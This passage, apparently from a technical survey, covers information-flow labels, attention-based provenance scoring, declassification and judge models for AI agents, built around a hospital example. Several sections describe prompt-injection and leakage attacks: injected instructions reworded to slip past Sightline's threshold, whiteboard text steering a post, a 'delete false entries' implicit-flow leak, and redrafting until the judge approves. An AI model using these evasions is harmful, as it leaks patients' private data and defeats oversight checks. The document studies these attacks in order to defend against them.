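I(U; Y₁, …, Yₙ) = Σ I(U; Yᵢ | Y₁, …, Yᵢ₋₁).

Each term is an average over all the beginnings the model might have generated. Adding up the scores for one finished poster includes only that poster's beginnings, so the sum would not measure the full flow.

Two different image tokens may look almost the same once decoded, so a large score could correspond to no visible change. This error is on the safe side if the decoder receives only the tokens and fresh random noise, because the finished picture then cannot reveal more about the photo than the tokens do. Measuring only the text would not be safe in a system like Qwen3-Omni, whose Talker also receives other features. The developer would have to measure the effect on the audio tokens.

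Some models would need a different formula. *Unified Multimodal Autoregressive Modeling with Shared Context* (2026) describes a model that predicts groups of visual codes in parallel, bit by bit, before a diffusion decoder generates the image. If the bits are predicted independently given the model's hidden state, F becomes a diagonal matrix with an entry q(1 − q) for each bit, where q is the probability that the bit is 1.

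Thresholds may not transfer between models either. *Studying Image Tokenizers as Visual Languages in Unified Multimodal Models* (2026) found that a tokenizer can reproduce images accurately without making their tokens easy for a shared model to learn. Because GIF depends on the model's token predictions, the same photo could score differently under two tokenizers, even if the posters looked alike.

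### Diffusion generators

A diffusion generator, which refines a picture from random noise, has no next token. Some versions add fresh noise at each step, which can be written as

xₜ₋₁ = m(xₜ, c) + σₜN.

Here xₜ is the unfinished picture, c is the embedded prompt or reference image, m is the model's refinement and σₜ is the amount of new noise. This is already close to a Gaussian channel. If J now describes how m responds to small changes in c, the equivalent of GIF for one step would be

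½ log₂ det(I + (τ/σₜ²)JJᵀ).

With τ = 1, eigenvalues 3 and 0, and σₜ = 1, this gives 1 bit, as before. Reducing σₜ to 0.1 raises it to ½ log₂ 301, or about 4.1 bits, because there is less noise to hide the influence of c. Adding up the values for all the steps and averaging over the random noise should give an approximate upper limit for the finished picture when τ is small. It is an upper limit because someone who saw every version of the picture would learn at least as much as someone who saw only the last.

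Other generators add no noise after the start, so σₜ is zero and the formula gives an infinite flow wherever c has any effect. A useful measure would have to account for the random starting point, or for how precisely an observer can measure the picture.

The hospital could also estimate influence without this mathematics by removing an input and generating the output again. For example, it could compare posters made with and without the whiteboard photo, using the same random seeds so that chance differences don't obscure the result. For an announcement, it could compare pitch and loudness as well as words. These comparisons only estimate influence. Even if they miss something, the hospital can label a poster public if it was generated from the style guide alone, the request contained nothing restricted, and the decision to publish did not depend on the photo.

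## What attention and gradients can certify about a flow

Regenerating an output without an input is a safe way to drop that input's label, but it requires extra model calls and may change the output. Inspecting the computation behind the original output to show that the input played no part in it would take less computation. The usual objection is that neural networks are too opaque for this, and *GIF* adds that an analysis requiring zero flow either labels almost everything or needs too much computation.

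In November 2026, Xu and colleagues tested this objection with Sightline, a tool that uses a text model's attention to judge which inputs reached its output. They also proved thirteen results about what such evidence can show, all verified in Lean. The results support part of the objection. A transformer's structure limits the routes information can take, but a weak signal along a route does not prove that an input was irrelevant.

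### Routes between tokens

A transformer keeps a vector for each token and updates it layer by layer. Most operations in a layer work on each token's vector separately, and only attention moves information between tokens. *A Mathematical Framework for Transformer Circuits* (Elhage, Nanda and colleagues, 2021) describes this as the basic job of an attention head, which reads from one token's vector and writes to another's. A fact in the voice memo's transcript can therefore affect a word of the announcement only if attention carries it there, directly or through tokens in between.

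At token t, a head gives each token i a weight aₜᵢ. The weights add up to 1, and the head's output is

oₜ = W Σ aₜᵢvᵢ,

where vᵢ is a vector computed from token i, called its value, and W is a fixed matrix. The head sets the weights by comparing a query from token t with a key from each token i.

A small change at an earlier token s can affect oₜ in two ways. It can change the value vₛ, which the head multiplies by aₜₛ. It can also change the key and so shift the weights, but the size of this effect is proportional to aₜₛ too. Xu and colleagues therefore get the bound

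‖∂oₜ/∂hₛ‖ ≤ aₜₛcₜₛ,

where hₛ is the vector the head reads at token s, and cₜₛ depends on the sizes of the head's matrices and vectors. For example, if aₜₛ = 0.001 and cₜₛ = 50, moving hₛ by 0.01 moves the head's output by at most about 0.0005.

To extend the bound to the whole network, they give each token an amount of taint, θ. It starts at 1 for the tokens of the input under study and 0 for all others. Each layer then updates it:

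new θⱼ = Λⱼθⱼ + ρⱼ Σ aⱼᵢcⱼᵢθᵢ, summed over all heads and all earlier tokens i.

The first term is token j's existing taint, and the second is the taint it picks up from the tokens it attends to. Λⱼ and ρⱼ bound how much the rest of the layer can amplify each term. The final θ bounds how strongly a small change to the input can affect the model's internal vector at an output position. If no chain of attention connects the input to that position, the bound is zero, and so is the local flow that *GIF* measures.

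Attention normally gives every token it can see a weight above zero, but software can force a weight to zero with a mask. *Can AI Keep a Secret?* (2025) proposes a mask that lets each token attend only to tokens at its own trust level or below. Russinovich (2026) showed in *What the Model Cannot See* that when every read of a passage is blocked, replacing the passage with any other text of the same length, however different, leaves all the model's internal values outside it identical to the last bit. The passage's length and position can still affect the output.

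In principle, a mask could also separate the outputs of a unified model. Whoever ran the hospital's model could block the poster's tokens from attending to the whiteboard photo, or to any token that had attended to it, while still letting the script's tokens use the photo. The poster would then get the same label as if it had come from a separate context. This requires control over the model's internals. Both papers concern language models, so the idea remains untested for pictures.

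### What the amount of attention can hide

Without a mask, all the attention weights are above zero, so analysts have to interpret them. A large weight may mean little. If a head's matrices turn every value into zero, the head contributes nothing, however strongly it attends. A second head can also cancel the first by writing the exact opposite. In one real program that Xu and colleagues examined, the model read both a query and a delimiter (a marker that separates parts of the prompt), but only the query determined the answer.

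Adding up attention across heads does not solve this. Suppose one head gives 60% of its attention to the memo and 40% to the style guide, and copies from each in proportion. A second head attends only to the memo and writes −0.6 times the memo's content. The memo's contribution is then 0.6 − 0.6 = 0, while the style guide's is 0.4. Both heads attend more to the memo than to the style guide, but only the style guide affects the output. Any score that never falls as attention rises would rank the memo at least as high as the style guide.

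Low attention weights can be just as misleading. Suppose a head divides its attention between a fixed token and an input whose value u is −1 or 1. The input's weight is σ(20u), where σ(x) = 1/(1 + e⁻ˣ). If u = −1, the weight is about 2.1 × 10⁻⁹, so nearly all the attention goes to the fixed token, and the model answers "open". If u = 1, the weight is almost 1 and the model answers "closed". A record of the run with u = −1 would show almost no attention to the input, even though the input determined the answer. Xu and colleagues compare this to the branch not taken in a conventional program.

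They found nothing so extreme in their own data. Each of the 11,746 inputs that reached Qwen3-8B's output received a weight of 1% or more from at least 11 of the model's 1,152 heads. The median input received that much from more than 1,000 heads.

A milder form of the effect occurs in trained models. *InversionView* (2024) examined a small transformer that added three-digit numbers. In one run, a head attended almost entirely to an 8 in the tens place of the second number. But its output also revealed that the tens digit of the first number was at least 4, because the head would have attended differently if that digit had been smaller. Such cases are hard to rule out in a large model. Transformer Circuits Thread, Anthropic's series on the inner workings of language models, lists the formation of attention patterns as an open question.

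### What gradients and removal can hide

Gradient and Fisher scores, including Geometric Information Flow, can also be misleading because they shrink towards zero as the model becomes more certain of its output.

Suppose a model chooses between "closed", with a score of 20u, and "open", with a score of 0. In the recorded run u = 1, so "closed" has a probability of σ(20), which is almost 1. The gradient of its log-probability is

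20σ(−20) ≈ 4.1 × 10⁻⁸,

and the Fisher score is

20²σ(20)σ(−20) ≈ 8.2 × 10⁻⁷.

Both suggest that the input is irrelevant, but changing u to −1 changes the answer to "open". Such certainty is common. For one in five of its outputs, Qwen3-8B gave its top choice of token more than 99% of the probability on average. It is typical of short decisions, which an agent may act on.

Removing the input avoids this problem when the answer changes without it. Like NeuroTaint's test, however, this method fails if the same information occurs twice. If the whiteboard photo and the voice memo both contain the information that the ward has measles, software that removes one item at a time could drop both labels from a notice that the ward is closed. Regenerating the notice without both items would expose the mistake.

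Removing an input also shows little whenever the model would probably give the same answer without it. If a token has a probability of at least 95% both with and without the input, removing the input changes the token's log-probability by at most 0.05/0.95, or about 0.053.

Xu and colleagues tested both weaknesses on text, using AUC to measure how well each method ranked inputs. When they added two more copies of a value to the prompt, the removal test's AUC fell from 0.93–0.97 to 0.54–0.69, while Sightline's was at least 0.99. On the most confident fifth of outputs, Sightline scored 0.91–0.96, and a version of GIF they extended from one output token to 32 scored 0.63–0.75.

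### How Sightline scores an input

Sightline analyses recorded model calls from programs that insert values, such as a user's question or a retrieved document, into a prompt template. It runs the model once over the prompt and the output. For each attention head, it measures the average and peak attention from the output to each inserted value, and that value's share of the attention to the whole prompt. Qwen3-8B has 1,152 heads, so this gives 3,456 numbers per inserted value.

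A logistic regression trained on labelled examples combines these numbers into one score. It can give a head a negative weight, so more attention from that head can lower the score. In the example with the delimiter, the query scored 5.7 and the delimiter −6.7.

The score covers only direct attention from the output to the input. On Qwen3-8B, direct attention accounted for a median of 71% of the effect of removing an input, and adding two-step routes did not improve accuracy. However, the models' thinking mode was off. A reasoning model could copy a fact from the memo into its reasoning and then read it from there. If the analysis did not count the reasoning as part of the output, direct attention might be a poorer guide.

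### A guarantee on average

Since no score can prove that an input was irrelevant, Xu and colleagues limit how often Sightline wrongly drops a label. They use conformal prediction, a statistical method that sets a threshold from past cases whose correct answers are known. The procedure is as follows:

1. Group the labelled calls into clusters. Each cluster is a family of related code repositories, because their calls may fail together.
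2. From each cluster, randomly choose a place in the code where at least one input reached the output, then choose one of those inputs.
3. Sort the scores of the chosen inputs from lowest to highest.
4. Set the threshold at the kth lowest score, where k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋, n is the number of clusters and α is the target miss rate.
5. In new calls, drop the labels of inputs that score below the threshold.

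With 299 clusters and a 1% target, k = ⌊0.01 × 300⌋ = 3, so the threshold is the third-lowest score. If a new cluster resembles the old ones, the score of an input from it that did reach the output is equally likely to have any of the 300 possible ranks. The score falls below the threshold only if it is among the lowest three, which has a probability of 3/300, or 1%. With fewer than 99 clusters, k would be zero and Sightline could not drop any labels.

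This works for any score, even a useless one, but a poor score removes few labels. If more than 1% of the inputs that matter score close to zero, the threshold must also be close to zero. Confident outputs cause this problem for gradient and Fisher scores. At the 1% target, the extended version of GIF removed only 0.6% to 12.1% of the unneeded labels, depending on the model.

The guarantee is also an average, so the miss rate can exceed the target for some kinds of output. In a separate test on Qwen3-8B with a 5% target, Sightline missed 10.1% of the inputs that mattered to the most confident fifth of outputs. Setting a separate threshold for each fifth can correct this. With a 1% target, separate thresholds kept the miss rate below 1% in every fifth and still removed 42.5% to 61.0% of the unneeded labels.

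### When new cases differ from old ones

The calculation requires the clusters to be exchangeable, meaning that swapping the new cluster with any old one would not change the probabilities. Grouping calls into clusters makes this more plausible because calls within a cluster can depend on each other in any way. *Beyond Aggregate Risk* (2026), which calibrates checks on agents' tool calls, instead requires individual fields with the same role to be exchangeable, even though several may come from one episode.

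An attacker who knew how Sightline worked could break this assumption by trying many wordings of an injected instruction until one both steered the model and scored like unused text. The 1% limit would not apply to that instruction, because the attacker selected it instead of drawing it at random from cases like the old ones.

*Robust Conformal Intrusion Detection via Traffic-Aware Calibration and Attack-Orbit Invariance* (2026) describes the same problem in network security, where attackers control some of the features that a detector examines. If defenders can sample the attacker's method, they can restore the guarantee by calibrating on traffic altered in the same way. Otherwise, the error rate can rise by as much as the total variation distance between the old and new score distributions, which ranges from 0 (identical) to 1 (no overlap). A distance of 0.05 could raise a 1% miss rate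 to 6%, and a distance near 1 would leave no useful limit on the error rate.

This can also happen among language-model agents. In *Conformity Breaks Conformal Prediction* (2026), an adversary defeated a check calibrated on clean data by exploiting the agents' tendency to conform to one another.

The risk is greatest for integrity labels, because an attacker may write the untrusted text, whereas patients do not word their records to evade a tracker. An attacker could also inject an instruction telling the model to disguise a record in its answer. Even without an attacker, a new model or type of document could invalidate the old threshold.

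### Results on unseen programs

Xu and colleagues trained Sightline on 8,105 pairs of inputs and outputs from open-source Python projects. They tested it on 4,918 new pairs per model, from 2,842 places in the code of 2,103 repository families. The four models were small, the largest having about 8 billion parameters. They could not record real values at this scale, so they had a language model propose plausible ones from the surrounding code. Three authors independently judged 95 of 100 such values plausible.

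The table compares Sightline with the best of seven other methods for each model. The accuracy score is the average of two F1 scores, one for inputs that reached the output and one for those that did not. Conservative merge scores about 47. An unneeded label is one that conservative merge adds from an input that did not reach the output.

| Measure (%) | Qwen3-8B | Granite 4.2 3B | Gemma 4 E2B | Nemotron 3 Nano 4B |
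|---|---|---|---|---|
| Accuracy score, Sightline | 86.0 | 84.1 | 86.7 | 81.1 |
| Accuracy score, best other method | 80.2 | 79.6 | 80.5 | 79.1 |
| Unneeded labels removed, Sightline | 65.6 | 58.5 | 61.6 | 43.9 |
| Unneeded labels removed, best other method | 29.4 | 22.4 | 37.7 | 26.8 |
| Unneeded labels removed, Sightline with the older projects' threshold | 56.2 | 54.4 | 60.1 | 43.8 |

The pruning results use a 1% target for the share of inputs that mattered but were missed, averaged over possible calibration sets. Sightline missed about 1%, even with a threshold from the older projects. A stricter threshold has at least a 90% chance of meeting the target for the particular calibration set in use. With that threshold, Sightline removed 33.7% to 58.0% of the unneeded labels.

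These miss rates depend on how the researchers decided which inputs had reached the output. They used three language models as judges, GPT-6 Astra, Claude Opus 5.5 and DeepSeek-V4.1, which compared their answers and settled disagreements by majority. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) introduced this procedure and reported some errors in it, including one case in which the judges marked a system prompt as ignored although it had shaped the style of the answer. Sightline's miss rate does not count influences that the judges overlook.

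In a test that did not rely on these judges, the researchers planted unique names, numbers and web addresses in prompts. Sightline identified the source in all 476 outputs that copied them word for word.

Sightline takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call. It needs access to a model's attention, which companies with closed models do not provide, but another model can read the recorded text instead. When the four test models read each other's calls, the accuracy score was between 4.2 points lower and 3.2 points higher than when a model read its own. With a substitute model, the theorem applies to the substitute's computation, not the one that produced the output. As with GIF, a clean substitute might therefore miss a tampered model's hidden signal.

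### Results on an agent under attack

The researchers also tested Sightline on text records of a Qwen3-8B agent facing AgentDojo's prompt-injection attacks. They examined 517 pairs of inputs and calls from 120 steps at which the agent called tools. They set a more lenient target, allowing the test to miss 5% of true flows.

Sightline removed 50.0% of the unneeded labels, with an actual miss rate of 3.9%. AttnTrace, another method based on attention, removed 38.3%, and none of the other six methods removed more than 15.7%. After Sightline removed labels, an integrity policy like FIDES's still blocked all 34 calls that carried out an attack.

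Zero failures in 34 calls is encouraging but limited evidence of security. If the calls were independent, this result would be consistent with a true failure rate of up to about 8%. The attacks also predate Sightline, so they weren't designed to evade it.

### How many labels this removes

Removing 44% to 66% of the unneeded labels has a modest effect overall, because only 12% to 14% of the inputs in the program data did not reach the output. The share of all labels removed is therefore between

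0.12 × 0.439 ≈ 5% and 0.14 × 0.656 ≈ 9%.

For every 1,000 labels, Sightline would correctly remove about 53 to 92. If it missed 1% of the inputs that mattered, it would wrongly remove about nine. The gain would be roughly half as large in the earlier collection, where Xu, Cheng and colleagues found that only 7.0% of 8,119 inputs had no visible effect.

Long, mixed contexts could benefit more. Programmers usually insert a value into a prompt because the task needs it, whereas an agent's conversation accumulates old emails, files and tool results. In Zhong and colleagues' privacy tests, conservative merge gave many tool calls unneeded labels. A hospital assistant that worked through a whole shift might have many items in its context that are irrelevant to the next poster.

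But removing an item's label does not necessarily make the poster's label less restrictive. If five irrelevant items are each open only to Ada and Ben, the poster stays restricted until the software removes all five labels. If the software has a 60% chance of removing each label, independently of the others, its chance of removing all five is 0.6⁵, or about 8%.

The software also has more chances to miss something in a long context. The 1% limit applies to one randomly chosen input that affected the output. If 20 restricted inputs affected an output and each had a 1% chance of being missed, the chance of missing at least one could be as high as 20%. The hospital would need to calibrate on similarly long conversations and limit the chance of missing even one such input per output.

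### Models with other routes

The attention theorem does not fully cover models that move information between tokens in other ways. State-space layers, used in some language models to process long texts with less computation, keep a running summary of what came before. In a Mamba2 layer, each token adds to this summary and determines how much of the earlier content fades.

Xu and colleagues prove that a token can affect later output in two ways. The output may use what the token added to the layer's summary of the text so far, much as attention uses a value. The token may also shrink the earlier content in that summary, even if the output uses nothing the token added. For example, suppose earlier text would contribute 10 units to an output, and a token multiplies the summary by e⁻². The contribution falls to about 1.35, so the token has changed the output by about 8.65 without adding anything.

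Nemotron 3 Nano has 42 layers, of which 21 are Mamba2 layers and only 4 are attention layers. Sightline reads only the attention layers, which may help explain its lower accuracy on this model. The other three models were slightly more accurate than Nemotron at judging Nemotron's calls, scoring 83.2 to 84.3 compared with 81.1. Masking attention is not enough to hide a passage in such a model, so Russinovich also had to recompute the running summary as if the passage were absent.

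Xu and colleagues tested only text, so the consequences for images have to be inferred. The theorem should apply to image tokens if a standard transformer generates the picture one token at a time. Sightline would need new training examples showing which pictures reflected which inputs, and the judges who labelled them could overlook a choice such as the blue palette for lung patients.

Diffusion generators depart further from the theorem's assumptions. They refine the whole picture repeatedly, so information can pass between any two regions and carry over from one step to the next. A version of the bound could add up the flow along all these routes, but it would probably become very loose after dozens of steps. Some generators also use convolutions, which mix neighbouring parts of a picture without attention, or condense the prompt into one vector that adjusts every part of the picture.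 An image editor may start from a noisy copy of the whiteboard photo. The photo's content would then be in the unfinished poster before the model computed any attention, so a low attention score for the photo could not justify removing its label.

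## When a label may be removed

Influence scores and repeated generation help to remove labels from outputs that do not depend on restricted data. Some outputs that do depend on it must still be released. If the voice memo reports a measles outbreak, visitors need to know that the ward is closed, even though only Ada, Ben and Cam may play the memo. Changing the closure notice's reader list from {Ada, Ben, Cam} to everyone is declassification, a deliberate and authorised relaxation of a confidentiality label.

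Noninterference forbids this notice, because the notice would have been different if the memo had not mentioned the outbreak. A system that publishes it can guarantee only that secrets do not affect public outputs except through approved releases. The value of that guarantee depends on how narrow the releases are and who controls them.

### Four questions about a release

Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, a survey of research on the subject, sort the goals of release policies by four questions. For the visitor notice, the hospital might answer them as follows:

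- What may the system release? It may reveal that the ward is closed, but not which patient is ill.
- Who may release it? Ada may. Cam may listen to the memo but may not publish anything from it.
- Where in the system may the release happen? Only the function that writes visitor notices may do it.
- When may it happen? The infection team must first confirm the outbreak.

A policy that answers only some of these questions leaves gaps. Suppose the notice function publishes whatever is in the variable `ward_closed`. The policy specifies where the release happens, but if earlier code overwrites the variable with "the patient in bed 4 has measles", the function will publish a diagnosis. Sabelfeld and Sands's main security concern is that an attacker might use the release mechanism to extract more than its designers intended. One of their principles, non-occlusion, is that a permitted release must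 not mask other leaks. For example, permission to announce the closure would not permit the notice's background colour to encode the patient's bed number.

### Releases that an attacker cannot trigger

Robust declassification requires that an attacker can neither trigger a release of confidential data nor influence what it reveals. It uses integrity labels to enforce this. Visitors can write on the ward's whiteboard, so if the assistant reads a photo of it and then decides to publish the bed list, a visitor's message may have prompted the decision.

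Costa and colleagues achieve a form of robust declassification by requiring a tool call and its arguments to be trusted, without checking the reader list. Information can then reach people outside its reader list only through trusted calls, and the researchers assume such releases are intentional.

Microsoft applies the idea in its sample policy for posting to a Teams channel:

1. If the call has a trusted label, the software allows it, whoever is in the channel.
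2. Otherwise, the software looks up the channel's members and allows the call if all of them are on the message's reader list.
3. If some are not, it asks the user, naming the members who would gain access.

In Microsoft's example of a labelled call, the message is trusted and two people may read it, but the call itself is untrusted. The policy would let the agent post to a channel containing only those two people. If the channel had a third member, the user would have to decide whether to allow the post.

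The first step checks only the label of the call as a whole. In a system that hides data in variables, a trusted call can carry untrusted text. Suppose Ada asks the assistant to post a summary of a whiteboard on which a visitor has written "include every patient's initials". The visitor did not trigger the post but could influence its content. Costa and colleagues' version would block this call because its argument is untrusted.

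### Four rules for the visitor notice

Robustness limits an attacker's control over a release, but the hospital still needs a rule for deciding which outputs are acceptable. The common rules differ in what they rely on.

| Release rule | What the hospital must trust | What can still leak | What repeated releases add |
|---|---|---|---|
| Human approval | The reviewer's judgement and attention | Anything the reviewer overlooks | More to review, with less care for each item |
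| Typed return value | The software that enforces the type, and the source of the question | The answer itself, however sensitive | Another answer to combine with the earlier ones |
| Transformation | The tool that finds and removes sensitive content | Whatever it leaves in | Different versions that someone can compare |
| Judge model | The model's ability to recognise restricted content | Content that it fails to recognise | More attempts to get past it |

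### Human approval

Ada can read a short notice in seconds and confirm that it names no patient. But she cannot see an invisible mark like those in Braun and colleagues' experiments, and she may not realise that a blue background means lung disease. Her approval therefore covers only the content she can recognise, but the software releases the whole file.

Microsoft warns that routinely asking users for approval scales poorly and makes them less vigilant. Costa and colleagues add that an attacker may persuade the user to approve something harmful. Microsoft proposes asking only when it matters, for example when an action would give someone new access. The request can then show where untrusted data came from, what the agent wants to share, and with whom.

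### Typed return values

The hospital could instead write the notice as a template with one blank. A quarantined model would listen to the memo and answer whether the ward is closed, or give the date it will reopen. Ordinary software would insert the answer.

In FIDES, constrained decoding enforces the type by letting the model generate only text that fits a given format. The label also records the type, and FIDES orders types by how much information they can carry:

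yes or no ⊑ a choice from a list ⊑ free text.

A policy can accept yes-or-no answers from restricted data and reject free text from the same source. But "Is the ward closed?" and "Does the patient in bed 4 have measles?" are both yes-or-no questions, and answering the second reveals a diagnosis. The question therefore has to come from someone with authority to release the answer.

The type label also does not track how many answers have been released. Under Costa and colleagues' definitions, the join of two yes-or-no types is still yes-or-no. If a tool combined several answers about a patient's date of birth, the result would keep the yes-or-no type, even though the answers together might identify the date. Limiting the total number of answers would require a separate counter. The hospital could also compute the answer once a day and show every visitor the stored copy, so repeated requests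 would reveal nothing new.

Garby and colleagues object that anyone auditing a run of FIDES cannot tell whether a small value that passed the policy was an intended release or a leak. LLMbda requires the program to state each relabelling explicitly. In their example, which concerns integrity, a quarantined model sorts an incoming email into one of a few categories. The program maps the model's output onto a fixed list, and an explicit instruction endorses the result for use as the subject line of a reply. The sender can influence which category appears there but cannot write the subject line.

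### Blurring, cropping and rewriting

A transformation keeps more of the original than a typed answer does. Suppose the hospital wants to publish a photo of a refurbished ward with the whiteboard in the background. Painting a solid rectangle over the patients' initials deletes those pixels. Blurring only mixes them, so if the initials are printed in a known font, someone could blur all 676 possible pairs of letters in the same way and see which result matches. Cropping leaves any clues that are still inside the frame, and a summary that omits a nurse's name may still identify the nurse by mentioning a wrist broken on Friday.

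A transformation can also protect data sent to an outside model. *RECAST* (Pei, Chen and colleagues, 2026) rewrites charts and recordings so that a remote model can solve a numerical problem without seeing the original content. For example, Ben might have a chart showing 48 measles cases in one month and 31 in the next, and want to know how far the number fell.

1. A model on Ben's computer turns the chart and the question into text.
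2. Another local model moves both to a new subject, such as umbrella sales, while preserving how the items relate to each other.
3. Local software replaces the numbers, perhaps with 62.4 and 20.75, and keeps the list of replacements.
4. The system makes a new chart from the rewritten text. For a recording, it uses a synthetic voice instead.
5. The remote model returns a short program that subtracts one number from the other. Ben's computer restores the original numbers, runs the program and gets 17.

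The researchers tested this on 2,000 charts and 2,000 spoken passages. A judge model compared each original with the request that the remote solver received. It counted a leak if the request revealed the original's meaning, its wording or which value belonged to which item, or if someone could link the request back to its source. The table gives percentages.

| Method | Chart accuracy | Chart leaks | Speech accuracy | Speech leaks |
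|---|---|---|---|---|
| Send the original to the remote model | 75.1 | Everything | 87.4 | Everything |
| RECAST | 70.2 | 8.0 | 80.0 | 7.9 |
| RECAST with an untrained rewriter | 66.4 | 37.9 | 71.0 | 41.6 |
| RECAST with GPT-5.6 as the rewriter | 70.3 | 5.2 | 81.0 | 1.2 |
| Best local model tested | 62.8 | 0 | 46.3 | 0 |

The leak rates depend heavily on the rewriter. GPT-5.6 leaked least, but using it would mean sending the original record to a remote model. For charts, RECAST was only 7.4 percentage points more accurate than a local model that disclosed nothing. The advantage was much larger for speech, where the local model had only 3 billion parameters.

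Across both kinds of input, the judge's leak rate was 7.95%. Human labels for a sample of requests gave an estimate of 8.70%, but three of the paper's own authors did the labelling. The judge's rate covers only requests to the solver, although the remote services that draft the new chart and synthesise the voice also receive rewritten content.

RECAST deliberately keeps some information. Larger numbers stay in order within three size bands, and related years move by the same amount. Whole numbers from 0 to 15 usually stay the same, because they are often counts or positions that the task needs. But in a hospital, a small number may be sensitive, such as a bed number or the number of patients with a rare disease.

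Pei and colleagues draw new replacement numbers for each request. The replacements depend on the original values only through their size bands and order, so averaging over many requests would not recover the larger values. Repeated requests are riskier for the rewritten text. If each request had an independent 8% chance of leaking, ten requests about the same chart would have a 1 − 0.92¹⁰ ≈ 57% chance of at least one leak, although the errors for one chart would probably be related.

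### Facts that remain in another modality

A video can identify someone by face, voice, words or surroundings. Blurring the face leaves the voice, which may be just as recognisable, and replacing the voice may leave the words unchanged. Pei and colleagues describe this last limit in existing speaker anonymisation. They also cite a 2024 study in which vision-language models inferred personal attributes from images that did not show the person.

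Separate labels for each track would handle the first problem. Suppose only Ada and Ben may see a video of a nurse, and the hospital blurs the face well enough to release the pictures on their own. The finished video still has the label

everyone ∩ {Ada, Ben} = {Ada, Ben},

because nobody has cleared the soundtrack. A system with one label for the whole file might wrongly treat the blur as sufficient.

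Joining labels does not help when two tracks are each harmless alone but together identify someone. Suppose the blurred figure's height and build match five of the ward's 40 staff, and the disguised voice's phrasing matches four. If only one person is in both groups, the video identifies that person. *MEMLEAK* found the same kind of leak across collections of photos. Whoever approves the release has to consider both tracks together, along with anything the hospital has already published.

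RECAST avoids some of these problems by discarding the original picture or recording and making a new one from text. The new recording can't reproduce the speaker's accent unless the text describes it. This works for charts and spoken problems because text can hold all the information needed for the task. It would be less useful for a photo of a rash, where the doctor needs the visual detail.

RECAST's test for whether someone could link a request to its source, which is closely related to re-identification, was the hardest to judge. The judge model agreed with the human majority on 88.3% of these decisions, compared with 93.8% for whether the request revealed which value belonged to which item. The human reviewers also agreed with each other least often on this test. But the reviewers compared each request with its original, whereas an attacker would have to find the source using other information.

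### A model as judge

A judge model can decide whether an output may be released by comparing it with the restricted data. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim et al., 2026) uses one in FLOWSEAL, a system for text-based agents that handle requests from outsiders. Users or software first register sensitive records and their owners. Whenever the agent tries to write or share something, ordinary code identifies the recipient, then allows the action if the recipient is trusted and blocks it if the recipient is untrusted. For anyone else, the code gives a separate judge model the proposed text and every tracked record that the recipient is not cleared to receive. The judge returns only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED".

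The judge does not see the agent's conversation, where an attacker may have presented the disclosure as routine work. In one of the researchers' attacks, an outsider shares a page that mixes true and invented facts about a patient and asks the agent to delete the false ones. The agent writes nothing secret, so an ordinary filter for outgoing text would find nothing, but the outsider can tell that the remaining entries are true. This kind of leak is an implicit flow.

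The researchers ran 105 scenarios three times each. The table shows the percentage of sensitive items that leaked with FLOWSEAL and with a detailed system prompt instructing the agent to check identities and get consent.

| Attack | System prompt only | FLOWSEAL |
|---|---|---|
| Ask the agent to fill in its part of a shared page | 52.2 | 0.5 |
| Ask the agent to delete false entries | 75.6 | 2.3 |
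| Send the request by email and collect the answer on a shared page | 43.8 | 2.2 |

FLOWSEAL's theorem states that nothing derived from a protected record can reach an uncleared recipient unless the judge wrongly answers "SAFE". The proof therefore shows that the code always calls the judge when it should, but it doesn't cover the judge's accuracy, which must be tested experimentally.

Shim and colleagues measured the judge's contribution by replacing it with a fixed answer. When the answer was always "BLOCKED", the agent completed none of the harmless tasks. When it was always "SAFE", the agent completed 79.4% of them, but the shared-page attack leaked 24.9% of the sensitive items. With the real judge, the agent completed 72.4% of the tasks.

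These harmless tasks did not call for any secret information. The judge was mainly correcting labels that conservative tracking had made too strict, although FLOWSEAL calls this step declassification. To release a protected record, the agent has to ask the record's owner. When the researchers told owners to agree to every request, FLOWSEAL delivered only 32.7% of the information the owners were willing to share, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for four prompt-based defences. The FLOWSEAL agent asked for consent less often. A consent rule can therefore block legitimate releases because the agent never asks.

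### How a judge fails

Shim and colleagues say paraphrase is the judge's main weakness. The judge may miss a sensitive value that the agent has reworded or placed inside a longer sentence. It may also block a harmless message that mentions a protected record without revealing its content. The researchers suggest, but did not test, that an attacker could split a fact across several messages that each look harmless. Giving the judge everything the agent had already sent to that recipient might help.

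When FLOWSEAL blocks a message, the agent can rewrite it and try again, and every new draft gives the judge another chance to make a mistake. If the judge had a 2% chance of wrongly approving each leaking draft, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of twenty would get through is 1 − 0.98²⁰ ≈ 33%. An attacker's words can also reach the judge if the agent copies them from a shared page into its draft. The study excluded prompt injection, so it does not show whether such text could cause the judge to answer "SAFE".

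The researchers also connected the system to real Gmail and Notion accounts. The deletion attack leaked 34.7% of the sensitive items against a defence that only advised the agent, and none against FLOWSEAL. This test counted only facts that appeared word for word, so it would have missed paraphrases.

Costa and colleagues describe FIDES as using ordinary code outside the language model to check each tool call, including its reader list where the policy protects confidentiality, so the model cannot override the check. Shim and colleagues, by contrast, say that FIDES leaves all its policy enforcement to the model, which would expose it to the same attacks.

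Shim and colleagues did not run FIDES because they could not fit it into their benchmark. With correct reader lists and the confidentiality policy switched on, FIDES should stop an agent from copying a patient's record onto an outsider's page. It would also block many harmless replies that FLOWSEAL's judge allows. To stop the deletion attack, the policy would have to treat deleting an entry as sending information.

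Judges can also work from only the passages that *GIF* scores as most influential. A small judge, Qwen3 8B, gained the most from this, with F1 scores 9% to 12% higher than when it read the full record. With three selected passages, it matched GPT-5.5 on two prompt-injection benchmarks at less than one eightieth of the cost. But the judge cannot assess a passage that *GIF* fails to select. The paper does not present such judges as a replacement for formal policies.

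For pictures and sound, a judge also has to detect the restricted content. FLOWSEAL's judge compares text with text. To check the hospital's poster, it would have to read small handwriting in the whiteboard photo and recognise the same information in a drawing. Li and colleagues' vision-language judge missed some changes that people could see, and a hidden mark would be even harder to detect. A text judge could check a written description of the poster, but only for details the description included. Checking a transcript of speech would likewise miss anything conveyed by tone.

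### Reclassifying one part of a label

The scheduling script has a two-part label that marks it as untrusted and allows only Ada and Ben to read it. If Ada checks the script and decides it is safe to run, that decision should not also make it public.

Garby and colleagues keep the two decisions separate in LLMbda. Write a label as ⟨i, s⟩, where i is its integrity part and s its confidentiality part. Endorsing a value with the new integrity i′ gives it the label

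pc ⊔ ⟨i′, s⟩,

where pc is the label of the program's current position. Ada's endorsement therefore changes

⟨untrusted, {Ada, Ben}⟩ to ⟨trusted, {Ada, Ben}⟩.

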